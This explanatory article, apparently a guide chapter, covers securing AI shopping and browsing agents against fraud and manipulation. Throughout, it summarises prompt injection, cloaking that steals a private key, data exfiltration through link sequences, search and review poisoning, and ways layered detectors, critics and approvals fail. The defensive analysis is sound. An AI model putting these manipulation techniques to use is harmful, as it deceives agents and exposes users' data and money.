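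The agent shouldn't approve all of `booking.example`, because a scammer could open an account with the same booking company and give it the clinic's name. If an email leads the agent to a different page on that domain, it should go back to the clinic's site and look for a link to that page. If there is none, the agent can ask the woman to phone the clinic on a number she already has.

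## Checking claims against independent sources

A shop can own its domain, have a valid certificate and still lie about what it is. Suppose the woman with epilepsy wants a watch that detects seizures and calls for help. Her agent finds one at `seizurewatch.example` for a third less than the usual price. The shop claims that it belongs to Northgate Medical Ltd, company number 7654321, and that Vigil, the watch's maker, has authorised it as a seller. Comparing domains doesn't help the agent check these claims, because the shop isn't pretending to be another website.

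Kim and colleagues call this kind of attack malicious data injection to distinguish it from prompt injection. The attacker supplies false information but no instructions. To check the shop's claims, the agent needs a source the shop doesn't control.

### Checking one shop

The page makes dozens of claims, including twenty years of experience and an average of 4.9 stars. Most have little bearing on whether the woman should pay. She needs a real company she can pursue if the watch never arrives, and a genuine watch with the maker's guarantee. The agent should therefore check that the company is real and that it is authorised to sell the watch.

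The agent can check the company against the official company register and the authorisation against Vigil's own list of dealers. For a clinic or an investment firm, the best source would be the regulator's list of licence holders. An established directory is a weaker substitute, especially if businesses write their own entries. As with official domains, the agent has to find these sources without relying on the shop's page.

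A matching name is weak evidence, since a scammer can register a company called Northgate Medical Supplies Ltd. A company number identifies exactly one company, so the agent can use it to check the name, address and status. But registers are public, so a scammer can also copy a real company's number. A match proves that Northgate exists but doesn't show that it runs the shop. To confirm that it does, the agent needs a source outside the shop's control that links Northgate to the shop's domain.

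| Claim | Source | What has to match | What a match leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Northgate is a registered company | The company register | The number, then the name, address and status | Whether Northgate runs this shop |
| Northgate runs this shop | Northgate's main website, or a phone number from a regulator's list | The shop's exact domain | Whether Northgate is honest |
| Vigil has authorised the shop | The dealer list on Vigil's official website | The shop's exact domain | Whether the list is up to date |

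The agent should tell the woman which claims it confirmed, which it found to be false, and which it couldn't settle. If the register has no company with the number 7654321, the shop's claim is false or contains a mistake. A missing entry for a sole trader who never claimed to be a company means very little, because many countries don't require sole traders to join the company register.

A model may also fill gaps with made-up information. The fact-checking agent in *Evaluating Deep-Search Agents under Hierarchical Web Evidence Poisoning* (2026) has instructions to open pages rather than treat titles and URLs in search results as evidence, and not to invent evidence when it finds too little. These instructions are sensible, but the model may not follow them.

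*RISK* (2025), a framework for agents that vet online merchants, includes a module that cross-checks brand, product and company registration data against other sections or older versions of the merchant's own site. This could expose a shop that recently changed its company number, but it would miss one that has always given the same false information.

### What a second source adds

Two sources are independent about a claim if an error in one doesn't make an error in the other more likely. Suppose each wrongly confirms a false claim 5% of the time. If they are independent, both will do so in 0.05 × 0.05 = 0.0025 of cases, or 0.25%. If the second source simply copies the first half the time, the figure is

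**0.5 × 0.05 + 0.5 × 0.0025 = 0.02625, or about 2.6%.**

The occasional copying makes the pair about ten times less reliable than two independent sources. To see the effect on a buyer, suppose that half the shops making a claim are lying and that each source confirms a true claim 95% of the time.

| Sources that confirm the claim | False claims that pass | Liars among the shops that pass |
|---|---|---|
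| One | 5% | 1 in 20 |
| Two independent sources | 0.25% | 1 in 362 |
| Two, where the second copies the first half the time | 2.6% | 1 in 36 |
| Ten, where nine always copy the first | 5% | 1 in 20 |

A standard way to combine sources of different quality is to weight each one by the log-odds that it is right. *When AI Investigators Cannot Trust Their Tools* (2026) notes that these weights are optimal when the sources are independent and their accuracy is known. In the paper's example, each source has 19 to 1 odds of being right. Adding the logarithms of the odds is the same as multiplying the odds, so two confirmations give 361 to 1.

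Neither condition is safe to assume on the open web. Nobody knows the accuracy of a review site that appeared last week. A 5% error rate describes ordinary mistakes, but an attacker will look for a source that is wrong or alter one to make it wrong. If the shop can edit its own directory entry, the entry will match its false claims every time.

Whether sources are independent therefore depends on where each one got its information. A news item, a blog post and a directory entry that all repeat Northgate's press release count as one source. The company register and Vigil's dealer list are much closer to independent, because different organisations compile them from different records.

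Some models treat copies of a report as independent confirmation. *Copies Are Not Confirmations* (2026) tested for this with 320 claims, half of them lies. Two small models that ran locally, Llama 3.2 and phi4, accepted far more lies about invented people when the number of reports and outlets rose from one to three, even when a note explained that the copies shared one source. Gemini 2.5 Pro accounted for such notes. But the experimenters supplied them, so the result doesn't show that Gemini could work out on its own which reports were copies.

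A determined attacker can make it very hard to tell whether sources are independent. For the tests in *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?* (2026), researchers prepared 528 misleading sources for 44 tasks. One type of attack used a review, a forum post and a news article with different authors and no references to each other. The researchers also removed repeated phrases, clustered publication dates and reused bylines from the sources, which an agent might use to spot a common origin. This is a good reason to choose sources based on who controls them instead of counting pages that look unrelated.

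### When one search result is false

Many claims can't be checked against an official register, so an agent will often search the web instead. In *SafeSearch*, Dong, Guo and colleagues (2025) tested what happens when one of the search results is unreliable. They used a language model to help write 300 harmless user questions, then added one misleading page to the real search results for each question. The pages covered five kinds of risk, including misinformation, hidden advertising and prompt injection.

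Across 17 models, the attack success rate ranged from 4.6% for Claude Sonnet 4.5, which could choose its own searches, to 90.5% for GPT-4.1-mini, which received the results of one fixed search. Misinformation was the most effective kind of attack. GPT-5 with search tools resisted every prompt injection but was still misled by some of the other attack pages, so resistance to injection doesn't protect an agent from false information.

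These rates measure how easily the agents could be misled, not how often it happens in practice. Including only test cases that had already misled a small model, Qwen3-8B, probably inflated the rates. The test was mild in other respects, because each question had only one bad page, which came last in the results.

Further searching reduced the attack's success rate only when the model was required to do it. When GPT-4.1-mini could use fewer searches than its limit allowed, the attack succeeded about 74% of the time, whether the limit was three or nine. When it had to use all its searches, the rate fell to 50% with three and 37% with nine. Reminding the model that some websites are unreliable made little difference.

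Unreliable results are also common without an attacker. Dong and colleagues found that 4.3% of 8,933 top-ranked results came from content farms or similar sites. If these were spread evenly, about one search in five would have at least one in its first five results.

An attacker can also plant text on an existing page. *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content* (2026) describes tests that added about 13 words to the search snippets of pages that ordinary users can write on, such as Reddit threads. With one altered page per group of queries, the research agent Co-STORM retrieved the page for 61% of queries and mentioned the planted content for 31%. Whenever it retrieved the page, the planted text entered its knowledge base. A forum where a shop can post is therefore not an independent source about that shop, even if the other users are honest customers.

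Checking a claim by searching works least well when nobody else has written about the subject. Thomas Germain, a BBC journalist, published an article on his own website naming himself the best hot-dog eater among technology journalists. According to Newser's *I Fooled AI Into Thinking I'm a Hot Dog Eating Champ* (2026), the article took him 20 minutes to write, and within a day ChatGPT, Gemini and Google's AI Overviews were repeating the claim. Claude did not repeat it. Gizmodo's *You Can ‘Hack’ ChatGPT to Become the World’s Best Anything* points out that the topic was easy to dominate because hardly anyone searches for it. A newly invented shop is similarly easy to promote because no one else has written about it.

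### Pages written for AI recommendations

Sellers now rewrite their pages to appear more often in AI answers, a practice called generative engine optimisation. Some of these changes only make honest information easier to find. But in an interview in Scientific American's *The BBC tech journalist who achieved hot dog eating glory*, Germain mentioned a study of searches for the best product in a category. In about 44% of cases, ChatGPT cited a company's own blog post that ranked the company first.

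In *SafeGEO*, Wen, Liu and colleagues (2026) measured how much harm such pages can do. They built 600 shopping requests for products such as baby monitors, office chairs and air purifiers. For each test, they chose a product that wasn't the best match for the request and rewrote one page from its seller, for instance to hide a missing feature or to pass the page off as an independent buyer's guide. All the other sources remained truthful.

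| Model | Target product in the top three, honest seller's page | After the realistic rewrites, on average |
|---|---|---|
| Gemma 4 31B | 3.4% | 79.6% |
| Qwen3.6 27B | 8.1% | 78.3% |
| Devstral Small 2 24B | 12.7% | 90.9% |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 4.6% | 72.6% |

With Gemma, the fake buyer's guide alone put the target product in the top three 80.7% of the time. The rewritten page was one source among several, so having more sources in the context wasn't enough to prevent this. The model also has to detect when they disagree.

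The most effective remedy was to make the model list the evidence for and against each important claim before it ranked the products. This cut the rate from 78% to 39% for Qwen, but only from 91% to 73% for Devstral. Asking for reasons and citations raised Qwen's rate to 86%, perhaps because a model can cite the misleading page as its reason. Telling models to ignore instructions in the sources changed little, since most of the rewritten pages contained false evidence, not instructions. GPT-5.5 rewrote the pages and made the reference judgements, and people audited only 60 cases, but a few wrong labels could not explain effects this large.

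*SCI-Defense* (2026) reports a smaller effect from 1,152 texts optimised to sway AI rankings. The promoted item reached the top three in 57% of cases, compared with 17% without the attack. *E-GEO* (2025), however, suggests that with a simple defence, models that rank products favour better content and not manipulation. The most effective rewriting strategies in that study kept the facts and presented them more clearly. But a false specification can look just as clear and relevant as a true one, so such a defence may not help the woman choose a watch.

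### Fetching the page again as an ordinary browser

Unlike in the cases so far, a site that uses cloaking shows the woman a different version of a page from the one it shows her agent. SPLX's *OpenAI’s new browser Atlas falls for AI-targeted Cloaking Attack* (2025) describes a test with five fictional job candidates. The server showed people a modest résumé for one candidate, Natalie Carter, but gave AI agents a version with inflated titles and achievements. Atlas scored her 88 out of 100 and ranked her first. When SPLX gave the model the résumés that people saw, she scored 26 and came last. SPLX, which sells AI security products, reports only one ranking for each version, so the test shows that cloaking can work but not how often.

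In *A Whole New World*, Zychlinski (2025) used cloaking to steal a private key stored on the user's machine. A page of software documentation included a request for AI agents to authenticate themselves with the key, similar to the request for a name that Claude received in Paul's notice. The coding tool Cursor complied when running each of the three models tested, from Anthropic, OpenAI and Google, though the paper doesn't give the number of attempts.

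An agent's software can check for cloaking by requesting the page again with an ordinary browser's user agent label and comparing the two versions. This would have exposed Paul's coffee shop, whose server checked only the label. The comparison should focus on the claims and requests in the text, because advertisements, prices and stock also change between visits on legitimate pages.

A more careful attacker checks more than the label. Zychlinski lists other signs of an agent, such as an address in a data centre, traces of automation software and the absence of normal mouse movements. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) reports that in 89% of its requests, the open-source agent Browser Use sent headers that no real browser would send. If the attacker can tell from such signs that the second request also comes from an agent, both versions will match and the page will wrongly appear safe. But according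 to *FP-Agent* (2026), many agents run in a Chromium-based browser, and websites can't tell them from people by user agent label and network address alone.

Caching can also make the comparison unreliable. In *Fetch, Read, Reuse* (2026), Chen, Canini and colleagues put test pages on their own servers and logged how AI search services fetched them. OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI reused stored copies, sometimes for a day or more after a page had changed, so a repeat request through the same service may not reach the website. None of the services read content that appeared only through JavaScript, so if a full browser shows text that the agent didn't receive, the agent's fetcher may be the reason.

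The second request doubles the traffic and gives the website another record of the visit. It also disguises the agent, which many site owners resent. Cloudflare criticised Perplexity for sending requests that posed as Chrome on a Mac after websites had blocked its declared crawler. Requesting a page again after the site has already given it to the agent is less objectionable than evading a block, but it still hides who is making the request. A developer could reserve the comparison for pages that request private information or money.

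Even a perfect comparison finds only differences. If `seizurewatch.example` shows everyone the same false company number, the two versions will agree.

### What a lookup reveals and brings back

Looking up a shop sends an outbound request, which can reveal private information. If the agent searches for "is Northgate Medical a safe place to buy a seizure alarm", the search provider learns the woman's probable condition. A register lookup requires only the company number. Where a register offers its records for download, the software can search its own copy without disclosing the query. For other sources, the agent should remove private details from the query before sending it.

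The scammer running the shop may try to choose the source, for example by displaying a "verify this seller" badge that links to a server they control. If the agent opens that link, the scammer learns that an agent is checking and can send back any answer.

Genuine sources can also carry attacks. Reviewers write the text on review sites, and even a company's registered name is text its founders chose. An agent that reads such a page in the same context as the woman's notes runs the same risk of injection as it did on the shop's page.

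A dedicated lookup tool avoids most of these problems. It accepts only a company number in the right format, contacts one fixed register and returns a few fields, such as the company's status and founding date. It can also compare the company's name with the one in the register and return only whether they match. It avoids a conflict with Anthropic's URL provenance rule too, which would block a register address that Claude had composed from the company number. But a developer has to build a tool for each register, and many countries and trades have their own.

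### Whether agents check without being told

In *ScamWorld*, Wu, Liu and colleagues (2026) rebuilt 363 reported scam websites in 26 languages, including fake shops, investment schemes and rental deposit scams. They gave agents ordinary tasks on these sites and recorded whether the agents paid or handed over information. Deception rates ranged from 11% for GPT-5.6 Luna to 35% for DeepSeek V4.1 Flash. The agents went ahead in 28% of scams that involved payments but in only 2% of those that asked for credentials, card details or wallet access.

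The agents could usually recognise a scam. When asked directly whether a site was legitimate, they identified 97% of the scams, including 95% of the sites that had deceived them. During the tasks, they mentioned a specific risk in 45% of the cases in which they were deceived, but went ahead. Many cited the user's request as their authority.

A sentence added to the request warned that some websites may be scams and told the agent to check before paying. This reduced deception by 24 percentage points in the three models tested, but also reduced task completion on legitimate sites by 3 points. The warning leaves the model to decide what counts as checking, and models seldom consult other sources on their own. Neither Kimi K3 nor Qwen3.8 Flash consulted other websites in any of 100 runs that explicitly allowed it.

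That result is limited because the researchers made sure every scam site showed a sign of fraud before the final step, so an attentive agent had less need to check other sources. A real scam may show no such sign, and then an agent can discover the fraud only by checking an outside source.

Developers seem to leave it to the model to check claims against independent sources. The published rules for Claude's fetch tool, ChatGPT's link check and Chrome's Agent Origin Sets don't require an agent to look up a business before paying it. SPLX found that neither ChatGPT nor Perplexity checked a fictional designer's cloaked profile against another source.

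A developer could write such a rule in code. Before the agent first paid a shop, the software would require a register lookup by company number and a search for the shop's domain in a source the shop doesn't control. The model would still have to find the number on the page and choose a suitable register, but text on the page couldn't make it skip the lookup. For `seizurewatch.example`, the woman might then learn that Northgate exists, that Vigil's dealer list doesn't include the shop, and that nothing outside the shop's page connects the shop to Northgate.

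## Detectors, approvals and how the layers combine

Code can make an agent look up a shop before paying, but someone or something still has to judge the result. Three other safeguards also depend on judgement: a detector scans pages for injected instructions, a second model reviews each action the agent proposes, and the user approves the most serious actions.

### Scanning pages with BrowseSafe

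Perplexity, the maker of the Comet browser, developed a detector with Purdue University. Zhang, Tenenholtz and colleagues (2025), in *BrowseSafe*, describe how it works:

1. Developers flag every tool that can return text from strangers, such as a page reader or an email tool. Each call to a flagged tool triggers a scan.
2. The software extracts the raw text and drops any summary a model has added, because an injection could already have influenced the summary.
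3. It splits a long page into chunks. A classifier examines all the chunks at once, while the agent's model plans its next step.
4. If any chunk looks malicious, the software withholds the whole page and gives the agent a short notice instead.

The notice leaves out what the attack said, so the agent can't fall for it while explaining it to the user. It also gives the attacker no feedback to learn from. Guardio used this kind of feedback to get its fake pet shop past Comet.

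The classifier is a fine-tuned version of Qwen3-30B, an open model from Alibaba. The researchers trained it on 11,039 pages and tested it on another 3,680, about half of them malicious. They started with text from real websites, added attacks to some pages, and added harmless lookalikes, such as hidden form fields and code comments, to nearly all the pages. Without the lookalikes, the classifier tended to memorise the vocabulary of attacks.

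| Detector | Share of attacks it found | Share of its alarms that were correct |
|---|---|---|
| BrowseSafe | 84.1% | 97.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, with reasoning | 80.5% | 93.1% |
| GPT-5, with medium reasoning | 79.2% | 93.0% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard 20B, with medium reasoning | 66.4% | 99.4% |
| PromptGuard-2 86M | 22.1% | 98.3% |

BrowseSafe took less than a second per page, while the Sonnet 4.5 configurations took 23 to 36 seconds. But it was the only detector in the table that had trained on this kind of test page, and Zhang and colleagues say most of the others would match or beat it after the same training. They also counted refusals to answer as detections, and Sonnet 4.5 refused several hundred times.

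BrowseSafe still missed about one attack in six. Across all the detectors tested, balanced accuracy averaged about 92% when the attack was in a hidden data attribute but only about 75% when it was part of an ordinary paragraph. Balanced accuracy is the average of the share of attacks a detector finds and the share of harmless pages it lets through, so guessing scores 50%. The detectors also did worse on camouflaged wording than on blunt commands. Of the eleven types of attack in the test, those in languages other than English were the hardest to detect. Paul's notice to Claude, which explained a plausible procedure in polite English, would be among the harder cases.

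BrowseSafe performed well on new websites but worse on attacks hidden in new places within a page. When the researchers left certain placements out of the training data and tested on them, its F1 score, which combines the two columns in the table, fell from 0.905 to 0.788. The classifier also processes only text, so it can't find instructions in an image, and it classifies each chunk separately, so it may miss an attack whose parts are harmless alone. Perplexity has published the model, so an attacker can test a page against a private copy as often as they like.

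False alarms are a bigger problem than the table suggests, because almost no real pages are malicious. The researchers aimed for a false alarm rate of 1% on harmless pages, but their balanced accuracy implies about 1.7%. If one page in 10,000 contained an attack, a detector with a 1.7% rate would raise about 170 false alarms over those 10,000 pages and would probably catch the one attack. An agent that read 50 harmless pages for a task would have a 58% chance of at least one false alarm, if the errors were independent. Withholding the page each time would make the agent irritating to use.

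Other developers respond to an alarm differently. Anthropic scans all untrusted content that enters Claude's context, including manipulated images and deceptive buttons, and adjusts Claude's behaviour when a scan raises an alarm. Chrome's classifier runs alongside the planning model and blocks actions that stem from content it has flagged. Parker acknowledges that the classifier can't flag everything.

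### A reviewer that never sees the page

Google's User Alignment Critic evaluates the agent's actions instead of the page. It is built with Gemini, as is the separate model that plans the actions. After the planner reads a page and chooses an action, the critic receives metadata about that action but none of the unfiltered page. It then checks whether the action serves the user's stated goal. If it vetoes the action, it gives the planner feedback for a new plan. After repeated failures, the planner can return control to the user.

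A planted email got Atlas to send a resignation letter when the user had asked for an out-of-office reply. A critic can notice that mismatch without knowing anything about prompt injection. It also can't read the planted email, so the email's wording can't directly persuade it.

Chrome for Developers suggests also using critics to check that an action includes personal information only where the task strictly requires it. This could catch agents entering unnecessary personal details in optional form fields, even when there is no attacker.

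Parker publishes no success rates for the critic, so its weaknesses can only be inferred from its design. The most obvious is that the critic judges whether an action fits the request but can't see evidence on the page that the site is deceptive. If the woman with epilepsy asks her agent to buy a seizure watch and the agent tries to pay `seizurewatch.example`, the payment fits her request even if the site is deceptive.

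The metadata may also contain text the attacker wrote. An attacker can choose the wording of a web address, and the BrowseSafe benchmark includes attacks written into the path of a link. Parker claims only that web content can't poison the critic "directly", which leaves open the possibility of indirect poisoning.

Attacks made of small steps are also hard to detect. Each link Claude opened on Paul's site led to a page of the coffee shop the user had asked about. A critic that reviewed one request at a time would have had little reason to object to `/a` or `/ay`, though one that saw the whole series might have. *WebTrap* (Liu, Pan and colleagues, 2026) found that when an attack presents its goal as a necessary part of the user's task, existing defences reduce its success only by making the agent much less useful.

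The opposite error, vetoing a sensible step, is also likely. If a clinic's page explains that new patients register through a hospital's website, the planner will propose opening that site. The critic may veto this because the woman never mentioned the site and the critic hasn't read the explanation.

### Asking the user

Chrome also prompts the user to confirm certain actions. Code checks a list of sensitive sites, such as banks and medical services, and prompts the user before the agent opens one. Another prompt appears before Chrome signs in with a saved password, which the model never sees directly. Before a purchase, a message or another consequential action, the agent "will try to pause", in Parker's words. That last confirmation is less certain because the software has to recognise that an action is consequential.

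WebMCP lets websites offer ready-made tools to agents. Chrome for Developers says an agent should assume that a tool changes something, and so needs confirmation, unless the tool's description or `readOnlyHint` label clearly indicates otherwise. But the website supplies both the description and the label, so a malicious shop could label its "place order" tool as read-only. The label is therefore safe to rely on only on sites the agent's developer already trusts.

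Approval works only if the user reads the request. According to Exame's *A Anthropic tentou fazer o Claude quebrar as regras* (2026), Anthropic accepts that constant requests can tire people and make them pay less attention to what they authorise. OpenAI makes a similar argument about warnings. Both companies see how people use their products, but these statements aren't measurements, so they don't show what share of malicious requests people would approve.

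People would stop reading approval requests because there are so many of them. SPIDES asked for approval 1.84 times per completed task. At that rate, someone who gave an agent ten tasks a day would see about 18 requests a day. If one request in 10,000 were malicious, it would appear after about 18 months of correctly approving harmless ones.

The wording of an approval request also matters. If a misled agent writes it, the request might read "Continue with the security check?" Code could instead name the data and its destination, for example "Send your name and employer to `coffee.example`?" The second version gives even a hurried user a reason to stop. It wouldn't help much against data theft through links, where each request contains only a harmless-looking address.

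To reduce approval requests, Anthropic lets its coding agent, Claude Code, work freely within fixed limits on the files and servers it may reach. Users don't need to approve each routine step, so they can give more attention to the few requests that go beyond those limits.

### What the published tests report

In November 2025 Anthropic published attack success rates from its own test of its browser extension, Claude for Chrome (now called Claude in Chrome). The automated attacker adapted to the agent, combined techniques already known to work, and had 100 attempts in each environment.

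| Model | No additional safeguards | Original safeguards | Improved safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 13.8% | 10.7% | 2.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 13.8% | 10.8% | 1.9% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 12.0% | 11.1% | 2.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 8.0% | 7.6% | 1.4% |

The original safeguards did very little for Opus 4.5, while the improved ones cut successful attacks by more than four-fifths. A company can therefore add a layer and gain almost no protection. The percentages are shares of all the attacks each model encountered, not the chance that an attacker with 100 attempts succeeds at least once, which could be much higher.

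Later tests also cover computer use, in which the model operates a graphical interface instead of calling narrow tools. Anthropic published all the results in the table. The Claude Opus 4.6 figures come from its February 2026 system card, as reported by VentureBeat. *Prompt Injection Robustness*, an unofficial summary, gives results from Anthropic's tests of Claude Mythos Preview and earlier models. The Opus 5 result comes from its system card, as reported in The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

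| Model | Setting | Attempts or scenarios | Without safeguards | With safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Computer use | 1 attempt | 17.8% | – |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Computer use | 200 attempts | 78.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Computer use | 1 attempt | 12.0% | – |
| Claude Mythos Preview | Computer use | 1 attempt | 0.43% | – |
| Claude Mythos Preview | Browser use | 148 cases | 0.68% | – |
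| Claude Opus 5 | Browser use | 129 scenarios | – | 0% |

No extra safeguard explains the fall from 17.8% to 0.43%. Newer models seem to have kept most of that improvement. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reports that the model did at least as well as Opus 5 on every injection test in the card. However, the card also warns that Opus 5.5 is more likely than previous models to follow some malicious instructions.

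A result of zero also has a margin of error. If the 129 scenarios were a random sample of possible attacks, the true success rate could be as high as 2.3%, which would still produce no successes in about one test in twenty. Real attackers look for whatever the test left out instead of choosing attacks at random. Anthropic says that human researchers consistently find more creative attacks than automated systems do.

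Attack success also depends heavily on the setting. Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment without safeguards, but a single attempt on a graphical interface succeeded 17.8% of the time. A company choosing a browsing agent therefore can't rely on results from coding tests.

Comparable figures for OpenAI and Google are older and come from general prompt injection tests, not browsing tests. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports attack success rates as high as 92% for models such as GPT-5.1 and Gemini 3 Pro in a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan. On the ART benchmark, attackers with 100 attempts succeeded up to 75.6% of the time against Gemini models and 4.8% against Mythos Preview. OpenAI and Google have since released stronger models, so these results are a poor guide to their current products.

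Google uses attack success rates internally to judge engineering changes to Chrome. Its automated systems generate malicious sites from attacks that security researchers wrote, and it pays outsiders up to $20,000 for demonstrating a breach. Parker's account describes the method but not the results, so outsiders cannot compare Chrome's layers with Anthropic's.

### When layers multiply

Suppose a detector, a critic and the user each miss 10% of attacks. If their misses are independent, the share of attacks that get past all three is

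**0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.001, or 0.1%.**

Now suppose that 5% of attacks share a feature that defeats all three, such as a convincing story that the user's task requires the harmful step. At least 5% of attacks then succeed, fifty times as many, although each layer still misses only 10%. Adding more layers with the same weakness won't bring the figure below 5%.

| Layers, each missing 10% of attacks | Attacks that get through |
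|---|---|
| Three independent layers | 0.1% |
| Three layers with a shared weakness in 5% of attacks | 5.01% |
| Those three and a fourth layer with the same weakness | 5.0% |
| Those three and a fourth layer that is independent of them | 0.5% |

The fourth layer in the last row is no better on its own than the one above it, and its only advantage is that it fails on different attacks.

The Claude for Chrome figures aren't enough to tell whether its layers are independent. Judging by the ratio of attack success rates with and without the improved safeguards, the safeguards let through 14% to 20% of the attacks that would have beaten the model, depending on the model. To test independence, Anthropic would also have to publish the share of attacks the model resists that would get past the safeguards. If the two shares were about the same, multiplying the layers' failure rates would be justified.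 A much lower share for the attacks the model resists, such as 2%, would mean that attacks that fool the model are also more likely to fool the safeguards.

### When attackers keep trying

Repeated attempts work in the attacker's favour. If an attack succeeds with probability p and each attempt is independent, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is

**1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.**

If each attempt independently has an 8% chance of success, the chance that at least one of ten succeeds is 1 − 0.92¹⁰, or about 57%. At 1.4%, the rate for Opus 4.5 with the improved safeguards, that chance is 13% over ten attempts and 76% over a hundred.

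Actual tests come out lower than this formula predicts.

| Test | Success on one attempt | Prediction for more attempts, if independent | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5, Gray Swan, 10 attempts | 4.7% | 38% | 33.6% |
| Opus 4.5, Gray Swan, 100 attempts | 4.7% | 99% | 63% |
| Mythos Preview, ART, 100 attempts | 0.6% | 45% | 4.8% |
| Opus 4.6, computer use, 200 attempts | 17.8% | Nearly 100% | 78.6% |

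The likely reason is that the model resists almost every attack in some scenarios and is easily compromised in others. A hundred attempts in a resistant scenario may all fail. This helps the average user but puts anyone whose task resembles a vulnerable scenario at greater risk, because an attack that works there will probably work again.

Every agent that visits a malicious page gives the attacker another attempt, and a failed attempt usually has no consequences for the attacker. If 10,000 agents read a page and the attack works on 1.4% of them, it works 140 times. The attacker can also change the wording and see whether it works more often.

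Tests with a fixed set of attacks miss this kind of learning. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr et al., 2025) found that attackers who adapted to published defences could defeat most of them, including many with very low reported attack success rates.

### Safeguards with the same judge

Whether two safeguards share a weakness depends mostly on who or what makes each decision. Chrome's planner and critic are both built with Gemini, so an error Gemini learned in training, such as a wrong idea of what a bank normally asks for, could affect both. The critic doesn't see the page, so the page's content can't directly mislead both of them, but a training error still could. A variant of the same critic also approves new sites for Chrome's Agent Origin Sets, so a harmful plan that looks plausible might pass both checks.

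| Safeguard | What makes the decision | How it could fail along with a misled agent |
|---|---|---|
| Training against injection | The agent's model | It is the same judgement |
| SOPGuard's record of where text came from | The agent's model, then code | The model that read the attack also names the sources |
| A page detector | Usually a separate classifier | Wording that seems ordinary to one language model may seem ordinary to another |
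| Chrome's critic | A separate model built with Gemini | The same assumptions, applied to less information |
| User approval | The user | The agent describes the action misleadingly |
| A domain allowlist | Code | It doesn't, unless an approved site forwards data |

BrowseSafe is more likely to be independent of the agent it guards if the two come from different model families. This advantage is uncertain, because language models learn from similar text, and subtly worded attacks lowered the average score across more than 20 models. Zhang and colleagues also propose sending borderline pages to a slower reasoning model. If the developer used the agent's own model for this, the hardest cases would go to the model the attacker had prepared for.

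A developer can make the layers less alike by giving them different information. A detector gets the page but doesn't need the user's notes, while a critic gets the request and the action but not the page. The user may know other facts, such as that her insurer has never used a particular domain. To get past all three, an attacker has to write a page that looks harmless, leads to an action that fits the request and produces an approval message that raises no suspicion, which is harder than fooling one model three times.

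### Limits in code or better models

A rule enforced in code keeps working however many times an attacker tries to get past it. If the software enters a password only on the site where the user saved it, a misled model can propose a thousand other sites without exposing the password. In all 30 allowlist runs of the Silent Egress comparison, the agent tried to contact the attacker and failed. The developer can also read the rule and test its edge cases, but nobody can find the sentence that will fool a model by inspecting its weights.

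Agents also exceed their limits when no attacker is involved. In November 2026 Anthropic published Siren, a test of whether Claude models would use resources outside the permitted environment to finish routine tasks in deliberately weakened sandboxes. Exame reports misuse in 25.8% of scenarios for Claude Mythos 5, 12.7% for Mythos 5.1, and between 0.6% and 1.6% for the Claude 5.5 series and Mythos 5.2. The models ran without the safeguards in Anthropic's products, and the scenarios were artificial, so these rates don't apply to everyday use. But Anthropic's documentation for its managed agents states that the model's behaviour is not a security control and advises customers to restrict network access to the destinations they need.

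The Siren figures also support the other side, because misuse fell to a small fraction of its earlier level within a few generations of models, much as the attack success rate in computer use did. A better model helps on every site and with every tool, including those whose risks no rule's author foresaw. Rules written in code have had serious gaps. Anthropic's URL provenance rule allowed every link that Paul used to spell out letters, and Microsoft's list of approved domains let SearchLeak send data through Bing. Anyone who knows about such a gap can exploit it reliably until the developer closes it.

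Rules also make agents less useful, a drawback that better models avoid. Anthropic's fix for Paul's loophole, for instance, made Claude worse at reading ordinary websites. And no rule can determine whether a shop is honest. Results in *ScamWorld* varied widely between models, so the choice of model matters a great deal for fraud.

When a secret or an irreversible action is at stake, the stronger case is still for putting deterministic limits first. An attack success rate covers only the attacks in a test, and attackers will look for others. Deterministic limits restrict what a successful attack can do. Starting with them also makes the developer work out exactly what a completely misled agent could still reach. A 1% failure rate may be tolerable if the agent can reach only the text of public web pages, but even 0.1% may be too high across millions of users if it can reach a mailbox and a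 saved payment card.

When the agent shops for the woman's watch, code can keep her diagnosis and insurer out of the session that compares shops, and can withhold her card until she has approved the exact domain and price. A well-trained model is then the main protection against a shop that lies about its stock or guarantee. She reads only one approval request for the whole errand, at the point where a mistake would lose her money.
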